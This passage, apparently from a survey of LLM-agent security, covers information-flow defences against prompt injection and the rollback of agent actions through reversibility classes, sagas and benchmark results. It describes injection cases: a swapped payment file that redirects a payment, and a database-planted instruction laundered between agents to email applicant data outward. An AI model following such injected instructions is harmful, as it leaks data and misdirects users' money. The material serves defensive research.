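Turning on CaMeL's policies cut task completion nearly in half and stopped attacks that had succeeded in fewer than 1% of runs. The benchmark is a weak test of the policies' benefit. In 97 of the 144 combinations of task and attack, the attack needs a step that a program for the user's task wouldn't contain, so planning before reading should defeat it without any policy. Garby and colleagues cite a similar drop in task completion for TypeGuard, a system like CaMeL that completed 15 of AgentDojo's 21 Slack tasks with policies off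 and 8 with them on. TypeGuard's developers observed that many of these tasks involve flows that no secure policy would allow.

Randori's advantage over CaMeL is harder to interpret because Randori enforces only a subset of CaMeL's policies, and its planning model can override the trust labels by endorsing data. Without endorsement, its score with MiMo-v2.5 fell to 54.2%. With only 16 distinct tasks, the uncertainty range for that score overlaps the range for CaMeL's 37.5%. The results do support allowing some exceptions, since three of the tasks require the agent to act on what it reads in a file.

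### Requests to follow a document

Both successful attacks on Randori involved one of those tasks. The user asked the agent to read a file and make the payment it described, but the attacker had replaced the file's contents with a different payment request. CaMeL failed on the same case in its developers' evaluation, though they don't count it among the attacks CaMeL is meant to stop.

Garby and colleagues describe two different cases in which recent systems still fail. CaMeL and Randori fail on the payment file, while CaMeL, TACIT and FIDES fail on the quoted hotel review, which is TACIT's one failure on AgentDojo. The hotel review failure is mostly a problem with the scoring, whereas the payment file failure would cost a real user money. Garby and colleagues nevertheless say that all four systems converge on the same remaining failures, which they read as a limit of information-flow control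 in general.

The payment file is a hard case because these designs assume that the user gives instructions and documents supply only data. A user who asks an agent to follow a document gives that document some of the user's authority. Costa and colleagues call a task *data dependent* if no single sequence of tool calls and final answer is right for every possible state of the data. "Do what this file says" is an extreme case, so a plan written in advance has to let the file's contents determine the actions.

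In the CaMeL reruns with policies off, when asked to follow a file's instructions precisely, the planning model wrote a loop with an instruction for each tool, so the file's contents determined the tool calls. One attack succeeded this way with each model, even though the planning model never read the file.

Labels don't help here, for the same reason that a forged bill could satisfy ToolFence's rule about sources. The real file and the attacker's replacement carry the same label, so a policy that uses only the label must allow both payments or block both, and endorsing the file's contents allows both.

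A developer can still reduce how much a document controls. Garby and colleagues describe an agent that sorts emails into a fixed set of categories and marks only the category as trusted. With eight categories, an attacker can influence at most log₂ 8 = 3 bits of the trusted output, which isn't enough to write an instruction. Santos-Grueiro (2026) proposes something similar for software development in *Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents*. The agent may use an automated build log to identify the file that failed, but not to choose the tool or mark a change as approved. Trusted code validates the file path and allows it in one specific argument.

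Santos-Grueiro tracks what influenced a choice as well as where its text came from. If text in a log leads the model to pick `write_file` from a trusted list of tools, the choice is untrusted even though the tool's name is trusted text. In 400 test runs on code repositories, the agent completed 231 tasks safely and no unauthorized action got through. This approach suits file paths better than payees, because a valid account number can still belong to a thief.

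### Labels that survive between agents

Data also has to keep its label when one agent passes it to another. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) built a system of three agents, each running CaMeL with no policies configured. The orchestrator had to get information about job applicants from a database agent and have a notification agent send a summary to a colleague, Julie, on Slack. The researchers planted in the database an instruction to email the information to an outside address.

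The database agent and the orchestrator followed their plans, since neither planning model received the planted text. But the orchestrator put the summary into its written request to the notification agent, which treated the request as coming from its user. The notification agent's planning model read the planted instruction and added the email to its plan. Peters-Gill and colleagues call this *boundary laundering*, because untrusted data became trusted when it crossed from one agent to another. They also prove that any such system is vulnerable to it if the system has more than one agent and an untrusted tool, and its agents can use tool results in their requests to each other.

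The proposed remedy, multi-CaMeL, splits each request into two parts. The `message` contains instructions, and the interpreter rejects it if it depends on any tool's output. The `variables` contain data, which keep their labels and stay hidden from the receiving agent's planning model. For the Slack task, the message would contain the instruction to send the supplied text to the supplied recipient, and a variable would hold the summary.

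The researchers tested this on a version of AgentDojo that divides each set of tools among several agents. Averaged over five models, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL in each agent and 0.0% with multi-CaMeL. All the attacks that succeeded against separate CaMeL agents used boundary laundering. The difference between 0.2% and 0.0% is a poor guide to how often boundary laundering would succeed in practice, because these attacks weren't especially strong (none succeeded against GPT-5.5, even with no defense). The worked example is better evidence that the security gap is real.

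CaMeL itself caused most of the drop in task completion. On AssetOpsBench, a test of industrial maintenance and monitoring work, running CaMeL in each agent lowered task completion by an average of 21.6 percentage points, and multi-CaMeL lowered it by a further 3.2. For the two strongest models, the corresponding drops were 13.4 and 0.85 points. Planted text couldn't add steps to a plan in these tests, but no policies were running, so the tests didn't establish whether secrets reached only permitted readers. If the outage agent asked a separate chat agent to post its summary, it would have to send the list of permitted readers with the text, and the chat agent would have to check that list.

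### The outage task under four designs

The table below compares four designs on a simple version of the outage task, in which the agent reads the log and posts a summary containing the key. In this version, someone has correctly labeled the log as secret, and some people in the channel aren't allowed to know the key. The object capabilities are plain references, without a wrapper like TACIT's, which adds a form of flow tracking.

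| Design | When the agent reads the log | When the agent posts the summary | Outcome |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tool allowlist | Finds `read_log` on the list | Finds `post_message` on the list | Allows both calls, and the key leaks |
| Argument rule | Confirms that the log belongs to the failing service | Confirms that the channel is `#on-call`, but accepts any text | Allows both calls, and the key leaks to that channel |
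| Object capability | Requires a reference to this log | Requires a reference that can post only to `#on-call` | Allows both calls, and the key leaks to that channel |
| Flow tracking | Labels the log with its permitted readers | Compares the summary's permitted readers with the channel's members | Blocks the message or asks someone, and would do the same if the summary omitted the key |

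## Which actions can be undone

If the outage agent does post the API key to Slack, someone can delete the message and the channel will look the way it did before, but the people who read it will still know the key. The company can cancel the key and issue a new one, which makes the leaked copy useless but takes work. If the agent had posted a confidential fact about a customer instead, the company would have no similar way to make the leaked information useless.

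### Restoration, compensation and irreversibility

*Restoration* returns the affected state exactly to what it was before. Zhai, Li and Wang (2026), in *Revisable by Design*, express this in symbols. An action *a* is reversible if there is another action *a*⁻¹ such that

exec(*a*⁻¹) ∘ exec(*a*) = id.

An action *a* is *reversible* if it has an inverse, *a*⁻¹, such that carrying out *a* and then *a*⁻¹ leaves the world outside the agent unchanged. *Compensation* is a further action that offsets the first without erasing it and leads to a state the user can accept, such as canceling a ticket for a fee. An action is *irreversible* if no compensation exists or if compensation would cost too much. These definitions depend on which further actions are available, so a service can sometimes make an irreversible action reversible by adding a way to cancel it, but a cleverer model can't.

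In *The Transaction Concept*, Gray (1981) separates *protected* actions, which a database can undo, from *real* actions, such as a cash machine paying out money. Once a database has committed a change, only a further "compensating transaction" can alter its effects. For example, an employer who has underpaid someone pays the missing amount. Gray compares this to the accountants' rule of correcting the books by adding an entry, never by altering existing ones.

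Someone has to decide what counts as adequate compensation. *A Formal Approach to Recovery by Compensating Transactions* (Korth, Levy and Silberschatz, 1990) gives the example of a customer returning a purchase to a shop. The sale may have prompted an order to the supplier and put the customer on a mailing list. The shop's policy determines whether to cancel the order and whether to give a refund or store credit.

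Researchers disagree about how to classify a sent email. Zhai and colleagues call it compensable, because the sender can follow it with a correction. *Can You Undo It?* (Waghmare and Sufi, 2026) classifies any intended delivery of content to outsiders as irreversible. Each view fits some emails, since a correction can fix a wrong meeting time but can't undo the disclosure of a secret. The stricter classification seems safer for a general-purpose email tool, because a checker often can't distinguish between the two kinds of email.

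Reversibility is separate from *severity* (how much harm an action does) and from whether the agent has permission to take the action. Canceling a patient's operation is compensable if it can be rebooked for a month later, but the delay could be very harmful. Sending a birthday greeting is irreversible and harmless. Reading a colleague's salary changes nothing, yet the agent may not have the right to do it. A payment that nobody can reverse may be exactly what the user asked for.

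### Five classes and three conditions

Waghmare and Sufi sort tool calls into five classes and suggest how much freedom an agent should have with each:

| Class | What recovery requires | Example | Suggested policy |
|---|---|---|---|
| R0, no effect | Nothing | Viewing the changes staged in Git | Act |
| R1, restorable | Writing back a saved earlier state | Editing a private file after saving a copy | Act, then notify the user |
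| R2, compensable | A known action with a limited, predictable cost | Creating a database table, which may leave a trace after someone removes it | Ask, or stay within a budget approved in advance |
| R3, hard to recover | A person's help, an outside process or unlimited effort | Clearing Git's list of staged changes | Ask every time |
| R4, irreversible | No recovery is possible | Publishing a message | Never act without explicit authorization |

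R3 also includes changes to access rights, credentials and the availability of a service. An action qualifies for R1 only if it meets three conditions:

1. A complete record of the earlier state exists.
2. The *principal*, meaning whoever the agent acts for, can already write that state back without anyone else's help.
3. No outsider has seen, received or acted on the changed state.

An audit log may meet the first condition but fail the other two. PocketOS's deleted volume would have failed the second, because Railway held a copy that PocketOS couldn't restore without Railway's help.

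Waghmare and Sufi's classifier gives a call the highest class that any of its effects requires, and it treats unknown calls as R4. Rules about arguments can lower the class, but they should recognize a specific safe form of the call instead of just looking for dangerous words. For example, a database query that begins with `SELECT` can look like a read but call a function that changes data. An operator can also lower some calls to R1 by saving the earlier state first. If the runtime can't confirm that the copy exists, the call goes back to its original class.

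The classifier does not make the copy or test whether a restore would work. It also relies on someone having identified all of a call's effects, which is hard when a deletion follows Windows junctions into live files.

### The later-writer problem

A *later writer* is a person or program that changes the same data after the agent does and before an undo. Suppose the data starts in state *s*, the agent makes change *a*, and a colleague then makes change *b*. The current state is *b*(*a*(*s*)). Restoring a saved copy returns the data exactly to *s*, but it also erases the colleague's change. The owner probably wants *b*(*s*), the result of the colleague's change alone.

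Korth and colleagues also judge compensation by comparing the result with a history in which the unwanted transaction never ran. They don't require the two to match, because a later transaction may have relied on the unwanted change. If an agent raises a price by mistake and a colleague quotes it to a customer, resetting the price doesn't withdraw the quote. A database could also undo every transaction that read the wrong price, then every transaction that read the results of those, but the number of transactions to undo can grow uncontrollably.

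Zhai and colleagues' formula for reversibility describes an undo that immediately follows the action. They list creating and deleting a file as a reversible pair, which is true only until someone else writes to the file. Replit's rollback has the same problem because it discards whatever the user has done since the checkpoint.

Waghmare and Sufi tested three ways to undo an agent's edit to a text file. The first restores the whole saved file. The second does so only if nobody has changed the file since the agent's edit. The third, a *three-way merge*, compares the saved original, the agent's version and the current version, and removes the agent's edit if it doesn't overlap with a later one. "Defers" in the table means that the procedure leaves the file alone for a person to sort out:

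| What happened after the agent's edit | Restore the whole file | Restore only if unchanged | Three-way merge |
|---|---|---|---|
| Nothing | Restores the original | Restores the original | Restores the original |
| Someone edited another paragraph | Erases the later edit | Defers | Removes the agent's edit and keeps the later one |
| Someone edited the same line | Erases the later edit | Defers | Defers |

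Each result was the same for all four versions of the file, which differed only in character set and line endings. Whole-file restoration was certain to remove later additions, since it replaces the entire file. The experiment shows how the loss happens, but not how often a colleague edits a file before someone tries to undo an agent's change.

In a fourth scenario, no saved copy was available. The classifier then treated the edit as R4, and the test program withheld it.

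TaskVM, the system presented in *Task-State Governance* (Yang, Pu et al., 2026), leaves such conflicts to the user. It operates ordinary applications through the screen and marks any value that a colleague has changed during the task. Before a rollback, it lists the effects it can't offset automatically. It restored the protected earlier state in four of the six trials that required it. Two ordinary agents failed to do so in all eight of their combined trials, but neither had a restore command.

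### Git, database and browser tests

Waghmare and Sufi also ran six real MCP tools for Git and the SQLite database, with two text variants for each scenario. Git saves versions of a project as *commits*. The documented way to undo a `git_commit` call is a *soft reset*, which moves the history back one commit and leaves the files unchanged. The reset restored everything they measured after an ordinary commit, but it failed in two other cases.

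In the first case, the commit completed a merge of two lines of work. While a merge is pending, Git keeps markers that identify what it is merging. The soft reset restored the history and the files but not these markers, so the next commit would not record the merge. In the second case, a contributor had added a commit after the agent's. Going back one commit removed the contributor's commit from the history and left the agent's in place, although the contributor's file was still on disk. Checking whether the agent's commit was still the latest, and deferring the undo if it was not, prevented this.

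In one SQLite test, an agent created a table, someone else added a row, and the undo deleted the table. The database then matched its original state exactly, so comparing the two states would not reveal that the row had been lost. Even if no one else had written to the table, SQLite kept an empty internal table that hadn't been there before if the deleted table numbered its rows automatically. This is why creating a table is R2 and not R1.

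For changes to existing rows, the researchers used a conditional update. Suppose an agent changed a price from 40 to 400. With made-up names, the undo would look like this:

```sql
UPDATE products SET price = 40
WHERE id = 7 AND price = 400;
```

If someone has since changed the price to 45, no row meets the condition, so the new price stays. In the tests, this kind of update restored the agent's row when nobody else had touched it, kept later changes to other rows, and did nothing when someone had changed the same value. It would still overwrite the price if a colleague had checked the 400 and decided to keep it, because the number alone doesn't record that decision. The tests ran every operation one at a time, so they didn't cover changes made during the undo itself.

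The browser tests asked whether an unsent draft survives when an agent closes a tab:

| Draft | Reopening the closed tab | Opening the page afresh |
|---|---|---|
| Unsaved text in a plain text box | Recovered in Chromium and Firefox, lost in Safari | Lost in all three |
| Text box that saved every change to the browser's local storage | Recovered in all three | Recovered in all three |
| Unsaved text in a rich text editor | Lost in all three | Lost in all three |

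The differences may not be due to the browsers, because the researchers operated Safari through its normal desktop interface but controlled the other two with automation software. Even within one browser, the outcome depended on how the page stored the draft and how the user tried to recover it, so no single class for "close tab" can be right for every page.

### MCP's hints and the registry

A runtime needs some way to find out which calls are reversible. The Model Context Protocol schema gives each tool four optional hints:

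- `readOnlyHint`: the tool doesn't modify its environment.
- `destructiveHint`: the tool may make destructive changes, as opposed to only adding things.
- `idempotentHint`: repeating a call with the same arguments has no additional effect.
- `openWorldHint`: the tool may interact with outside entities, as a web search does.

When a server gives no hints about a tool, a client should assume that the tool can modify things, may be destructive, isn't safe to repeat and reaches the outside world. A post by Model Context Protocol (2026) acknowledges that many servers omit these hints and that clients vary in how strictly they apply the cautious defaults. A dishonest server can also label a file-deleting tool read-only. The post therefore recommends relying on sandboxes and network controls for guarantees.

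Even accurate hints don't describe how to undo an action, since the schema has no field for an undo command, its cost or its deadline. Posting a secret isn't destructive under the schema because it only adds something, but nobody can undo the disclosure. Deleting a file a second time changes nothing further, but the file may already be permanently lost.

Waghmare and Sufi built a registry that classifies 536 tools from 20 MCP servers. It labels 333 tools R0 (no effect), 31 R1, 18 R2, 39 R3 and 115 R4 (irreversible). More than half of the 203 tools that have an effect are irreversible by these labels.

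MCP's hints were converted into classes so that they could be compared with the registry. Read-only tools became R0, and any other open-world tools became R4. The remaining tools became R3 if they were destructive and R1 if not, so no combination of hints produces R2. The two methods disagreed on 118 of the 481 tools that could be compared. The hints gave a higher class than the registry for 85 of them and a lower one for 33.

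Some of these disagreements would change what an agent may do alone. If it must ask before any action at R2 or above, 20 tools would need approval under the registry's labels but not under the hints. Ten of these are labeled irreversible in the registry but marked read-only by their servers. For another 41 tools, the reverse is true, and only the hints would require approval. These figures don't show which method is more often right, because the registry's labels are drafts written with AI assistance.

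The only human review so far gives reason to doubt the registry's middle classes, R1 to R3. Sufi, a coauthor, rated 148 tools, mostly by approving batches of ratings that an AI had proposed. Only 75 ratings matched the registry's, and most of the rest were higher. They matched for 58 of the 68 tools that the registry labels R0 or R4, but for only 17 of the 80 in the middle classes, including just one of the 31 labeled R1. The R1 mismatches matter because R1 is the class that lets an agent change things without asking first. Some of the AI's suggestions were wrong, so a mismatch doesn't prove that the registry is wrong, but an R1 label isn't enough reason to give an agent more freedom without testing the recovery.

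### Replaying recorded attacks

Waghmare and Sufi then applied their rules to 2,158 recorded runs from AgentDojo and τ²-bench. They compared a simple read/write rule, which asks for approval before any call that changes something, with a *session guard*. Once the agent has read data, the guard also assigns R4 to any call that could send data out, unless the operator has approved the destination.

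An attack achieved its goal in 47 of the runs, and the researchers could identify the call responsible in 29 of those. The session guard would have asked for approval before all 29 calls, and the read/write rule before 18 of them. In the 1,209 runs without an attack, the guard would have asked 1,904 times and the read/write rule 1,895 times.

All 11 extra calls were web requests, which look like reads but can leak a secret in the address of the requested page. When the researchers treated web requests as ordinary reads, the guard's result also fell to 18. The improvement is therefore better evidence for tracking what an agent has read than for the five classes.

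Approval requests rose by nine overall, or 0.5%, but the burden grew more in some settings. The two rules gave identical totals on τ²-bench, which supplied most of the harmless runs. On AgentDojo's Slack tasks, where all the extra attack calls occurred, approval requests rose from 34 to 47 across 21 harmless runs, while on AgentDojo's office tasks they fell slightly. Both rules also require approval often. Of the 770 harmless runs in which the agent had completed its task, only 119 would have finished without an approval request under the guard.

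A request for approval stops an attack only if the person refuses, and Anthropic's paid testers usually approved. The recordings all came from one older model, Claude 3.7 Sonnet, and replaying them can't show what an agent would have tried after a refusal.

### POLAR's search for an inverse

Kang, Cho and colleagues (2026), in *POLAR*, describe a program that allows a call only if it can first find a way to reverse it. The program works in four steps:

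1. For each tool that changes something, an expert records in advance which other call would reverse or offset it, and how confident they are in this, as a weight *w* between 0 and 1.
2. When the agent proposes a call, POLAR uses these records and the current state of the database to look for a sequence of calls that would undo it.
3. It scores each step of the sequence. An exact inverse scores *w*. A tool that reverses its own effect under some condition also scores *w* if the condition holds, and otherwise 0. Compensation scores *w*(1 − *ℓ*), where *ℓ* is the loss it leaves, such as a cancellation fee. A step that uses up something irreplaceable or has an effect outside the system scores 0.
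4. The sequence gets the score of its weakest step. POLAR refuses the call if the score is below 0.80 or if no sequence exists.

For example, compensation with *w* = 0.9 and *ℓ* = 0.05 scores 0.855, so POLAR allows the call. With *ℓ* = 0.2, the score is 0.72 and POLAR refuses it.

Kang and colleagues tested POLAR on τ²-bench with six models and 150 attempted runs for each combination of model and domain. The table gives the average task score, on a scale from 0 to 1, first without POLAR and then with it:

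| Agent's model | Airline tasks | Retail tasks | Telecom tasks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Nemotron 9B | 0.277 → 0.387 | 0.168 → 0.135 | 0.133 → 0.081 |
| Llama 3.1 8B | 0.291 → 0.473 | 0.047 → 0.076 | 0.009 → 0.062 |
| Qwen3-8B | 0.351 → 0.462 | 0.213 → 0.113 | 0.030 → 0.068 |
| Gemini Flash-Lite | 0.370 → 0.478 | 0.101 → 0.076 | 0.012 → 0.011 |
| gpt-oss-120B | 0.527 → 0.453 | 0.455 → 0.213 | 0.093 → 0.113 |
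| Qwen3.5-27B | 0.660 → 0.541 | 0.383 → 0.173 | 0.327 → 0.267 |

The score rose in 8 of the 18 combinations. The four weaker models did better on airline tasks, while the two strongest did worse there and much worse on retail tasks. These scores measure whether the agent completed its tasks, not how much harm POLAR prevented.

The search for an inverse may not have caused even the airline gains. In a separate test with Qwen3-8B, POLAR was allowed to accept only exact inverses. No airline tool has one (for example, rebooking a canceled flight creates a new reservation number), so POLAR refused nearly every change. The score still rose by 0.087, compared with 0.080 for the full system. A weak agent probably makes enough wrong changes that blocking almost all changes helps.

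POLAR's losses on retail tasks show the problem with allowing an action only if it can be undone. The calls it refused most often were returns and exchanges of delivered orders, because its records listed them as having outside effects. Customers ordinarily make such requests, and Kang and colleagues suggest that refusing them explains the lower scores. POLAR has another mode that asks the user to confirm a call instead of refusing it, which seems to suit these requests better, but the surviving records were too inconsistent for a fair comparison.

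Across all its tests, POLAR refused 1,745 calls, 910 because it found no inverse and 833 because of an outside effect. It never executed any of the inverses it found. It checks them against the database's state before the call, so an inverse that looks valid then may later fail or overwrite someone's work.

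## Reversing a sequence of completed calls

An agent booking a trip may have paid for a flight and a hotel by the time the car rental fails. The trip is then only partly booked, and undoing it takes several calls. A database could avoid this by running the whole job as one transaction, which takes effect completely or not at all. But it would typically lock the records involved until the job ended, which can keep other customers waiting for hours. *SAGAS* (Garcia-Molina and Salem, 1987) proposed a looser arrangement for long jobs, and most designs for reversing an agent's work borrow from it.

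### Steps and compensations

A *saga* is a long job divided into smaller transactions, T₁ to Tₙ, each of which commits on its own. Each step Tᵢ has a compensating transaction Cᵢ, although the last step doesn't need one if the saga ends when it commits. The system guarantees one of two histories:

T₁, T₂, …, Tₙ

or

T₁, T₂, …, Tⱼ, Cⱼ, …, C₂, C₁, for some 0 ≤ j < n.

In the second history, the system compensates for the completed steps in reverse order. For the failed trip, the agent books the flight, books the hotel, cancels the hotel and cancels the flight.

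These steps compensate without restoring the old state. In Garcia-Molina and Salem's airline example, canceling a seat subtracts one from the current number of reservations, which keeps any bookings that other customers have made since. Other people can also see a saga's partial results, so a customer who finds the flight full may buy a ticket elsewhere before the agent gives up its seat. AWS's *Saga patterns* describes compensation as going back to the previous data state, but sagas don't guarantee that.

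The order matters because later steps can depend on earlier ones. Suppose an agent creates a folder (T₁) and moves the only copy of a contract into it (T₂). C₂ moves the contract back and C₁ deletes the folder. If C₁ runs first, it deletes the contract too. Undoing the steps in reverse order prevents this, though it can be stricter than necessary. If the hotel and flight bookings don't depend on each other, the agent can cancel them in either order.

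After a failure, *backward recovery* compensates for the completed steps, while *forward recovery* carries out the missing ones. If a bank's program crashes halfway through adding interest to accounts, the bank would rather finish the job than take the interest back. A program can also combine the two by saving its state between steps. If it saved its state after T₁ and crashed after T₂, it can run C₂ to compensate for T₂ and continue from the saved state, giving the history T₁, T₂, C₂, T₂, T₃ and so on.

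All of this requires the compensation's code and inputs to survive the crash. Garcia-Molina and Salem suggest storing the code in the database before the step it reverses commits. An agent has the same need, since it can't cancel a hotel booking if the reservation number was only in a context it has lost.

### Failed and missing compensations

If ten compensations each succeed 95% of the time, and their outcomes are independent, the chance that all ten succeed is

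0.95¹⁰ ≈ 0.60.

The agent would therefore fail to undo at least one call in about 40% of its rollbacks. To raise the chance of a complete rollback to 95%, each compensation would have to succeed about 99.5% of the time.

However, independence is doubtful because an expired credential or an outage can stop several cancellations at once. If one shared cause determined all ten outcomes, the compensations would all succeed in 95% of rollbacks and all fail in the other 5%. At the other extreme, if no two failures ever happened together, one compensation would fail in half of all rollbacks. The 95% figure may also be too high, because a compensation runs only after something has gone wrong, and whatever broke the original step may break its compensation too.

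Retrying a compensation helps with temporary failures, if repeating the request does no extra harm. It doesn't help with a bug, because the compensation will probably fail the same way each time. The saga can then neither finish nor cancel. A programmer can prepare by writing a second version of the compensation that works differently. Otherwise a person has to intervene.

Some steps have no compensation. arc42's *saga pattern*, a guide for software architects, divides steps into three kinds. *Compensatable* steps have a compensating action. The *pivot* is the step after which the saga must go forward. *Retriable* steps come after the pivot and are designed to succeed eventually if repeated. For example, if the flight is nonrefundable, a booking program should reserve a refundable hotel and car first, then buy the flight, then email the itinerary.

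That arrangement requires knowing the steps in advance. Many agents choose each call after seeing the result of the last one, so the runtime doesn't know which calls will follow and can't move the nonrefundable flight booking to the end. It also can't rely on a programmer having written a compensation for every possible sequence.

### Undo calls from a model

In *GoEX*, Patil, Zhang and colleagues (2024) made an early attempt to supply the missing compensations. They argued that people often find it easier to judge an action's result than to review the action beforehand. Their runtime, also called GoEX, therefore lets an agent act first and gives the user a way to undo the action.

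For calls to web services, GoEX looks up each call's reversal in a table. If the table has no entry, a model writes the reversing call, and GoEX records whether it worked. Patil and colleagues admit that this guarantees nothing, but say it lets the model be "wrong at most once". One mistake may still be too many if it involves a customer's only database. A success also doesn't prove that the same reversal will work with other arguments. For example, Patil and colleagues note that knowing `delete_slack_message` reverses `send_slack_message` isn't enough, because the delete call may also need the number of messages to remove. Developers who need a guarantee can fill in the table themselves and restrict the agent to the calls in it.

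For databases and files, GoEX can test a reversal before anyone relies on it. A model writes the action, the reversal and a test, and GoEX runs them in an isolated container. The database test uses a small imitation of the real database, also written by the model, because copying the original would take too many resources. Testing should catch commands that don't work. But if the model is wrong about what the action does, its test may contain the same error. The database test also leaves out changes that other people may make to the real database.

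When an action can't be reversed, GoEX uses *damage confinement*, which limits potential harm by restricting the agent's access. It searches the user's request for the name of a service and supplies only that service's credentials, so a request to send a Slack message doesn't give the agent access to a bank account. This coarse check doesn't prevent the agent from messaging the wrong person on Slack. Patil and colleagues describe a working program but don't report how often its reversals succeed.

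*SagaLLM* (Chang and Geng, 2025) applies sagas to groups of agents. In its travel example, a model proposes itineraries and the user picks one. The system then turns the itinerary into five steps: a flight from San Francisco to Berlin, a hotel there, a train to Cologne, a hotel there and a flight home. The compensation for each booking is to cancel it. SagaLLM also records which steps depend on which, and under what conditions, to work out which bookings a failure affects. After canceling those, it has the model replan that part of the trip.

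In long tasks, models tend to lose track of bookings, the reasons for them and their dependencies, so SagaLLM stores these details outside the model's context. Chang and Geng say that a failed job returns to its original state, but this is only loosely true, because cancelling the flight in their example can carry a fee.

Chang and Geng's tests of SagaLLM provide little evidence about canceling real bookings. They used four scheduling problems from REALM-Bench, a set of planning tasks, and mostly presented individual schedules instead of success rates. In one problem, friends are on their way to a wedding when an accident triples travel times around the airport. DeepSeek R1's new plan had a driver leave for the airport at 1:05, although under the original plan he had already arrived there at 12:40. SagaLLM's record of past actions is meant to prevent this kind of error. Chang and Geng say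 that only SagaLLM handled the accident correctly, but they also describe the schedule from OpenAI's o1 as feasible, but less precise than it could have been. These examples are reasonable evidence that agents need an external record of what has happened, but they don't show that the right compensations would run after a booking failed.

### Recovery outside the model

In *Robust Agent Compensation (RAC)*, Perera, Hapuarachchi and colleagues (2026) criticize SagaLLM for relying on a model to write the workflow's code, choose each compensation and find its inputs. A mistake in any of these steps can leave in place a booking that should have been cancelled. They also found that an unexpected failure could send SagaLLM into a resource-intensive cycle of replanning.

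RAC gives more of this work to the runtime:

1. It records every tool call in a permanent log, with the call's inputs, result and status.
2. If a call fails for a reason that looks temporary, RAC waits and retries it.
3. If that doesn't work, a model looks for another tool that could do the same job.
4. If there is no usable alternative, RAC uses the log to work out the order of the completed calls and compensates for them, starting with those that depend on others.
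5. It adds a report of the failure and the rollback to the agent's context, so the model knows what is no longer in place.

RAC looks for each compensation first in settings supplied by the agent's developer and then in a field that Perera and colleagues added to MCP's tool descriptions. This field might pair `book_flight` with `cancel_flight`, for example. If neither source specifies a compensation, RAC asks a model for one, as it did in most of Perera and colleagues' tests.

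On five REALM-Bench problems whose descriptions listed the possible failures, RAC used between 9,000 and 33,000 *tokens* (the units of text that a model processes) per problem, while SagaLLM used between 52,000 and 250,000. But a plain agent with no recovery system also solved all five problems in every run, usually with fewer tokens than RAC. These results are stronger evidence against elaborate advance planning than for RAC's rollback.

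Perera and colleagues then wrote three harder problems with failures that the instructions didn't mention. The table shows how many of three runs succeeded, first with Gemini 2.5 Flash and then with GPT-5.4:

| What goes wrong | Plain agent | Agent with recovery instructions | SagaLLM | RAC |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Machines fail temporarily | 0 → 0 | 3 → 3 | 1 → 1 | 3 → 3 |
| Machines fail permanently | 0 → 3 | 0 → 3 | 2 → 0 | 3 → 3 |
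| The third of three flight bookings fails | 0 → 0 | 0 → 0 | 1 → 0 | 2 → 0 |

RAC did best overall, but the flight problem is the best test of reversing a sequence, because the agent has to cancel two completed bookings. RAC cancelled both in two of three runs with the weaker model and in none with the stronger one. Perera and colleagues suspect that hallucinations caused the failures. They do not report running this problem with handwritten compensation pairs, which would have helped show whether the failures came from the model's choice of compensation.

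The comparison with SagaLLM also needs some caution, because Perera and colleagues couldn't run its published code and repaired it themselves after its developers didn't reply. In an extra test on the permanent machine failures, with no limit on effort, the repaired version used 5 million tokens and ran about 34,000 unnecessary compensations before giving up. This shows how badly replanning can go wrong, though the original program might have behaved differently.

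RAC also has two weaknesses that a better model wouldn't fix. The first is that it treats a tool as having no side effects if it can't find a compensation for it. Perera and colleagues defend this with the example of a command that prints text. Printing can't be undone, but raising an error for it would interrupt ordinary work. However, RAC would treat an email tool the same way, so it could report a complete rollback after the agent has sent a confidential message. Waghmare and Sufi's rule of treating unknown calls as irreversible is safer, although it would interrupt more work.

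The other weakness is that, in RAC's published pseudocode, the first failed compensation ends the rollback and the user gets an error report. Stopping is sensible if the remaining cancellations depend on the one that failed. In the flight problem, however, the bookings are unrelated, so one failed cancellation could leave the traveler paying for another flight that RAC could have canceled.

### Repairs to cloud services

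*STRATUS* (Chen et al., 2025) applies undo to a narrower job, repairing faults in cloud services. Separate agents detect, diagnose and try to repair a fault, and a fixed set of stages controls which agent acts next. STRATUS records each attempt's actions on a *stack*, a list whose newest item is removed first. If the repair fails, an undo agent reverses the actions in that order, and the system can then try something else.

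The rule behind this, *Transactional No-Regression*, roughly requires that a failed attempt leave the service no worse than it was before. Undo here limits damage and also lets each new repair start from a known state instead of whatever state the last attempt left.

Across several models, STRATUS solved repair problems in two benchmarks, AIOpsLab and ITBench, at least 1.5 times as often as earlier agents. The comparison is between whole systems, so it doesn't show how much of the gain came from undo. *Advancements in Cloud-Native Systems* (2026), a review of research on reliability, recommends safety rules that allow agents' actions to be rolled back, but it cites only STRATUS for that recommendation.

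This method suits cloud repairs better than travel bookings. Many repairs change settings, such as how many copies of a program are running, which an agent can restore without asking another company for a refund. But undoing a bad repair doesn't help a customer whose order failed while the repair was in place.

### Invitations that have already gone out

Sometimes only one step in a sequence is wrong, and reversing everything would waste good work. *DART* (Yang, Li and colleagues, 2026) examines when a runtime can safely redo that step alone. In its example, a scheduling assistant has two subtasks. The first searches three people's calendars and lists possible meeting times. The second picks a time and sends the invitations.

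Suppose the first subtask searches calendars and finds Tuesday at 10 and Wednesday at 2, and the second invites everyone for Tuesday. The search turns out to have used an outdated copy of one person's calendar, and that person is busy on Tuesday. The runtime can restore a checkpoint from before the search and search again, and the new list might contain only Wednesday and Thursday. The assistant's records would then be correct, but everyone would still have an invitation for Tuesday.

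The runtime did nothing that its own rules forbid. Yang, Li and colleagues call such a rollback *controller-legal*, meaning that the software can carry it out, and distinguish this from whether the result makes sense. Their system, DART, is for agents whose developers have defined a fixed set of states and permitted moves between them. It first identifies the failed *instance*, which is one particular run of a subtask. It then looks for a *recoverable boundary*, a point from which that instance can safely resume. A boundary must meet four conditions:

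- **Decidable:** The runtime can tell exactly which instance the boundary belongs to. If the assistant has searched twice for the same meeting, the record must distinguish the first search from the second.
- **Closed:** The subtask has reached a complete handoff. A finished list of times qualifies, but a list based on two of the three calendars doesn't.
- **Separable:** Resuming from this point repeats work only within the failed instance. Redoing the search must not reopen an unrelated task that the assistant finished earlier.
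- **Controllable:** The developer's policy on side effects allows a rollback past this point. A policy might allow the assistant to discard a draft but not to roll back past a sent invitation.

DART saves checkpoints when an instance starts and when it reaches suitable boundaries. After a failure, it restores the latest checkpoint that passes two further checks. One applies the policy on side effects again. The other asks whether any committed step has used the failed instance's output. If W(p) is the set of data that instance p writes and R(q) is the set that instance q reads, DART treats q as dependent on p when

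W(p) ∩ R(q) ≠ ∅.

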